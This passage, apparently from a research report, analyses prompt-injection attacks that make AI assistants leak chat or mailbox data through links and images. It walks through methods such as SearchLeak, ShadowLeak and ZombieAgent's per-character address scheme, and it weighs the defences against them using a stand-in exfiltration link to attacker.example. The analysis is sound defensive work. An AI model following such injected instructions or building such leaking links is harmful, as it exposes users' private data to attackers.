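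Checkmarx demonstrated a zero-click leak in which Copilot Chat sent a secret key from a developer's environment through an image. Microsoft replied on 4 November that this did not meet its definition of a vulnerability because the attack required several actions that users don't take by default, did not work reliably and triggered warnings. Microsoft also assumes that people at work review and trust the code they choose to run. Checkmarx objected that Microsoft was neglecting an obvious safeguard, a strict limit on where images can load from. It expected Microsoft not to fix the one-click version either.

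Microsoft did fix a one-click leak in another Copilot product a few months later. Permiso's *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH* describes the attack, which Permiso reported in January 2026. Hidden instructions in an email made Copilot look up the user's recent Teams messages while summarising the email, and put them in a link under a fake security alert. Microsoft reproduced the attack within five days, finished patching it on 11 March, and then listed the flaw as CVE-2026-26133 in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. Microsoft had also fixed Logue's diagram button in 2025, whereas OpenAI's bug-reporting programme turned down Radware's report, so a required click doesn't by itself determine how a vendor will respond.

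The usual severity score for software flaws, which runs from 0 to 10, takes into account whether the victim has to click. SearchLeak, another attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, also needs a click, but at a different point. Taler (2026) explains in *SearchLeak* that the victim clicks a link to Copilot's search page on Microsoft's own website, and Copilot follows the attacker's instructions in the link's query string. It searches the victim's mailbox and outputs an image whose address contains an email's title. The browser requests the image before Microsoft's safeguard can disable it, and Bing passes the request on to the attacker.

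In SearchLeak, the user clicks a link that the attacker wrote, and the click delivers instructions to the assistant, whereas the click in a Link Trap sends the user's data out. A user who inspected the SearchLeak link before clicking would find no private data in it, because Copilot wouldn't yet have searched the mailbox.

Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) gives SearchLeak a score of 6.5 and lists user interaction as required. The US National Vulnerability Database scored it 7.5, assuming no interaction was needed, according to CVEfeed's page on the flaw (2026). The two assessments are otherwise the same, so requiring a click lowers the score by one point. Microsoft's assumption is correct, since the victim has to click. Microsoft still rates the flaw "Critical".

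EchoLeak, which required no interaction, scored 9.3, according to Lutra Security's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025). The click explains only part of the difference between its score and SearchLeak's, because Microsoft also judged that EchoLeak could affect other systems and allow some tampering with data. A flaw that requires a click can still score well above 6.5. The one Permiso found scored 7.1, according to Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-24950* (2026). Varonis' *CoSnitch*, published in August 2026, describes a one-click leak in the consumer version of Copilot. The United Nations University lists that leak at 8.8.

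## Defences, and what each does to a Link Trap link

The link `https://attacker.example/note?d=QW5u` can be used to test each defence. Suppose the attacker registered the domain yesterday, so no security company has examined it. The characters after `d=` are something the user typed earlier in the chat, encoded in base64, and the assistant has hidden the address behind the word "reference".

### Trend Micro's advice

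Trend Micro advises users to inspect the final prompt for instructions to collect information and build a link. This can work when someone pastes in a prompt from a forum, and it takes only a minute. In Keysight's example, the prompt included a visible request for a link containing a summary of the chat.

The advice fails against indirect prompt injection because software assembles the final prompt after the user asks a question, and the user never sees it. The developer in PromptArmor's Slack demonstration had no reason to know that the attacker's message existed.

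A company can instead use software that inspects prompts, such as Trend Micro's product. OpenAI writes that such filters don't usually catch fully developed attacks, because recognising one is as hard as recognising a lie, often without the necessary context. Its example is an email that reads like a colleague's note about a restructuring and asks for an employee's details to be sent to a "compliance validation system". Google uses such filters for Gemini, according to its *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), which gives no figure for how many injections they catch.

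Trend Micro also advises users to verify an address before opening it. A user who hovers over "reference" would see an unfamiliar domain and could stop there, but a phone has no mouse pointer to hover with. Many ordinary links also contain long strings of meaningless characters, so `QW5u` doesn't look alarming. The user has to check the address without sending it anywhere, because a link-scanning service that opens the page would deliver the data to the attacker. Copying the address and deleting everything from the question mark onwards would remove the data in this example, but not data in the path.

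### The model's own resistance

If the model ignores the injected instructions, it never writes the link, and the user loses nothing. Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* describes a test of Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, that Anthropic published in August 2026. An outside company, Trajectory Labs, used 72 injection scenarios that Anthropic had not seen. None of its 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5.

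If the 720 attempts were independent, zero successes would be compatible, at 95% confidence, with a true success rate of up to about 0.4%. If repeated attempts at the same scenario always end the same way, there are effectively only 72 tests, and the limit rises to about 4%. The agent was running in "auto mode", in which software decides whether an action can go ahead without the user's approval, so the result measures the models and that software together. In a Link Trap the assistant only writes text, so a control on actions might have nothing to block.

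Willison wanted more independent confirmation of the result. He has long argued that "99% is a failing grade" in security, because an attacker can keep trying until something works.

Developers can also instruct a model not to produce dangerous output. This takes almost no effort, but the model may not follow the instruction, as in Lan and colleagues' tests. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) describes an assistant in Google's online programming notebook that was instructed in its system prompt not to display images. Rehberger got it to display one anyway by asking it to join fragments of text that together made a Markdown image.

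### Blocking images or removing links

A content security policy is a set of rules that a website sends to the browser. The rules can restrict which servers images load from. Microsoft added one to Bing Chat in May 2023, after Rehberger reported that images could leak data, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. Gemini doesn't display external images. Either measure blocks the example address if the assistant writes it as an image, and users lose only pictures from other websites.

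Neither measure blocks the same address when it appears as a link, because both control what the chat page loads, not where the user goes next. After Google fixed the image leak in Colab, Rehberger showed that a link could still leak the chat and the code in the user's notebook.

Even for images, the policy fails if an attacker can receive data through a permitted site. Willison gives two examples in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*. The email assistant Superhuman allowed images from a Google domain that also hosts Google Forms, and a form can record data placed in its address. Salesforce's policy still listed a domain whose registration had expired, so researchers registered it and received customer data there.

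Salesforce then stopped its agent from producing links to untrusted domains. This would block the example link, because `attacker.example` wouldn't be on the list of trusted domains. Such a list suits an assistant that needs only a few business sites, but it would keep a general assistant from citing most of the web.

OpenAI offers a stricter setting, Lockdown Mode, for people at high risk. In this mode, ChatGPT browses only cached copies of web pages and may not display images in its answers, according to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* says that with cached browsing, no live web request leaves OpenAI's network. These limits make it much harder for ChatGPT to leak data by itself, but they don't cover the request that the user's browser sends when the user clicks a link.

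Amazon removed links from Amazon Q for Business's answers, replacing each address with "[URL not displayed]". In December 2023, Rehberger had shown that a text file could make Amazon Q write a "Sign In" link containing a summary of the user's messages. Embrace The Red's *AWS Fixes Data Exfiltration Attack Angle in Amazon Q for Business* reports that Amazon deployed the fix on 29 December, 25 days after the problem was reported.

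Removing all links from the answer stops the example link completely, since the user has nothing to click or copy. It also removes harmless links, including those the user needs to check the answer. The filter has to catch every way of writing a link. EchoLeak got past Microsoft's filter with a less common Markdown notation, and Logue used a diagram.

### Reputation lists and confirmation pages

Checking links against a reputation list inconveniences the user much less. When Safe Browsing has flagged a link, Gemini replaces it with the words "suspicious link removed". The example link gets through because its domain is a day old and nobody has reported it.

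Colab instead sends clicked links through a Google address, which shows a confirmation page before the user goes on to the other site. With the example link, the data would reach the attacker only if the user continued past that page. The user has to make an extra click on every outside link, harmful or not. Tenable's *The Trifecta* reports that Gemini also redirected links through a Google address.

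Colab's page didn't appear for links to Google's own domains. Anyone can host a small program on one of those domains through the Apps Script service, so Rehberger put his there. After one click, the program received a name and email address from the chat and the notebook's source code. Trend Micro's advice to check that a link leads to a trusted source would not have helped much, since the domain belonged to Google.

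People also get used to approving requests. Anthropic's article on auto mode, which Willison quotes, includes an experiment with 1,053 paid developers. Partway through a session, the experimenters replaced one permission request with a request to run a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6% of the developers refused it. This suggests that a warning that appears constantly and is usually irrelevant would stop few chat users. The figure doesn't predict how many would continue past Colab's page, because the developers were approving commands rather than opening links in a chat.

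### Checking where an address came from

Two other defences test the whole address instead of the domain. A URL provenance check tests whether an address in the answer was copied unchanged from a source that cannot have built it from private data. An address the user typed would pass. The example link fails because the attacker's text contained the address only up to `d=` and the model added the rest.

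Anthropic applies a similar rule to the tool Claude uses to open web pages. When the tool appeared in September 2025, it could fetch only addresses already in the conversation, such as those in the user's messages or in search results. Ordinary code checks each address, so the wording of an injection can't change the result. However, Willison noticed that many developers write programs that put outside text in the "user message", where an attacker's address would count as the user's own.

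In July 2026 Ayush Paul found another gap. The tool could also follow links on pages it had already fetched, so Paul built a website with a link for each letter, each leading to another page of the same kind. He wrote on the site that Claude had to find the user's profile by following the links that spelled their name. Claude never composed an address, but its choice of links revealed the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic closed the gap by stopping the tool from following links on fetched pages.

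This rule controls what Claude opens, so by itself it doesn't affect a link that Claude writes for the user to click. A developer could run the same comparison on every link before displaying it, which would remove the example link but keep citations copied exactly from search results. It would also remove useful links that the assistant composes itself, such as a search page with the user's city in the address.

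That possibility weakens Google's reply to Checkmarx that the leak through links was infeasible to fix. It may be infeasible to remove every harmful link while keeping every useful one, since both kinds can contain the user's data. But a company willing to lose some useful links can remove addresses that the model has composed.

In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) lists "URL sanitization" among Google's rule-based defences, which the company can update faster than it can retrain a model. Gavish doesn't say which URLs the rules remove, so it is unclear whether they would catch the example link.

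### From ShadowLeak to a public index

OpenAI tried a rule about altered web addresses before it adopted a stronger one. Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025) describes the attack of the same name that prompted the first rule. An email contained hidden instructions for ChatGPT, which had access to the user's Gmail account and could open web pages. When the user asked for a summary of the inbox, ChatGPT added personal details from other emails to the attacker's web address and opened it from OpenAI's servers.

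A simple version worked about half the time. Radware raised that rate considerably by making the request sound urgent and the address look like part of a compliance check. Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025, and OpenAI fixed it in early August, according to ThaiCERT's *“ShadowLeak” Vulnerability Exposes Gmail Data via ChatGPT Deep Research* (2025).

OpenAI then restricted ChatGPT to opening addresses exactly as supplied. That would stop ChatGPT from opening the example address, but it could still open addresses supplied by an attacker. Radware got round the restriction with ZombieAgent, an attack in which the email listed a complete address for every letter and digit, plus one for a space. ChatGPT spelled out the private data by opening these addresses unchanged, one after another.

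Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also made separate addresses for each position in the text. This takes 36 × *b* addresses for a block of *b* letters and digits, or 576 for a block of 16. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) had already described a similar leak that sent one character per address. It could send only ten characters per prompt because ChatGPT would open no more than ten addresses.

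OpenAI fixed ZombieAgent on 16 December 2025. After the fix, ChatGPT would open a link from an email only if the address appeared in a well-known public index or the user had typed it in the chat, according to *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026).

### OpenAI's public-URL check

In January 2026 OpenAI described the general form of this defence, a public-URL check. A crawler program visits public web pages and records their addresses in an index, without access to anyone's conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT fetches an address automatically, software checks whether that exact address is in the index.

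The example address fails even if the crawler has recorded `https://attacker.example/note`, because the crawler hasn't recorded the full address with `?d=QW5u`, which ChatGPT added during a private chat. Because the domain's reputation doesn't matter, this check avoids a problem with OpenAI's older one, url_safe, which always accepted addresses at bing.com. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) explains that Bing's search results use bing.com addresses that redirect to other websites, so an attacker could use one to reach a site of their own.

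When an address isn't in the index, ChatGPT either looks for another website or shows the user a warning titled "Check this link is safe". The warning shows the address with a note that the link may share data from the conversation, and lets the user copy or open it. This is more informative than a general notice about leaving the site, but a user who sees `QW5u` still can't tell that it means "Ann" unless the warning also shows the decoded text. In its March post, OpenAI says it shows users the information a request would transmit, but doesn't explain how it presents encoded data.

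OpenAI's written guarantee is only that it will prevent the agent from "quietly leaking" private data "when fetching resources", which covers automatic requests but not a user's clicks. Some evidence suggests that the check covers clicked links too. The warning has an option to open the link, and Tenable found that the older check ran on ordinary links as well as images. The example link would therefore probably trigger the warning in ChatGPT, but the user could still open the link.

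The check is less disruptive than removing all links, because most published pages that an assistant cites should already be in the index. New pages and addresses made for one person would trigger warnings. OpenAI chose to check exact addresses partly because it expected a strict list of approved sites to cause so many false alarms that people would learn to ignore them.

OpenAI also says that the check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy or prevent a website from deceiving the user. An ordinary phishing page can pass if its address is public. Embrace The Red adds that OpenAI's developers have to remember to use the check in every product. The older check was missing from ChatGPT's apps for Mac and iPhone.

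### What an approved link can still reveal

An attacker can also use addresses that are already in the index. Rehberger points out that a fairly large website probably has 36 indexed pages, enough for one per letter and digit. The attacker could specify in the injected instructions which page stands for which character.

If the model picks one of *N* approved addresses and the user clicks it, the attacker learns at most log₂ *N* bits, where one bit is the answer to a yes-or-no question. For 36 addresses, that is about 5.2 bits, compared with about 53 bits (16 × log₂ 10) in a random 16-digit number. This calculation is original to this report, not taken from OpenAI or Rehberger.

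| Approved addresses | Most bits per click | Fewest clicks for a 16-digit number |
|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.0 | 54 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 11 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 6 |
| 10,000 | 13.3 | 4 |
| 1,000,000 | 19.9 | 3 |

With 36 addresses, the attacker needs 11 clicks only if they use an efficient code. At one digit per click, they would need 16 clicks. Without the check, a single click on the link in Keysight's example would have sent 115 bytes, or 920 bits.

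An agent can open 11 pages in a row without anyone noticing, so Rehberger suggests that OpenAI keep copies of fetched pages or stop the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. In a Link Trap, the user would have to click 11 links presented as references, and few people would click that many.

Short secrets are harder to protect because an attacker can prepare an approved address for each possible value. Two addresses are enough to reveal whether a user has mentioned being pregnant, and 10,000 would reveal a four-digit PIN in one click. The attacker would first have to get those 10,000 pages into the index, but none of their addresses would contain anything private, so the link would pass the check and look normal even to a careful user.
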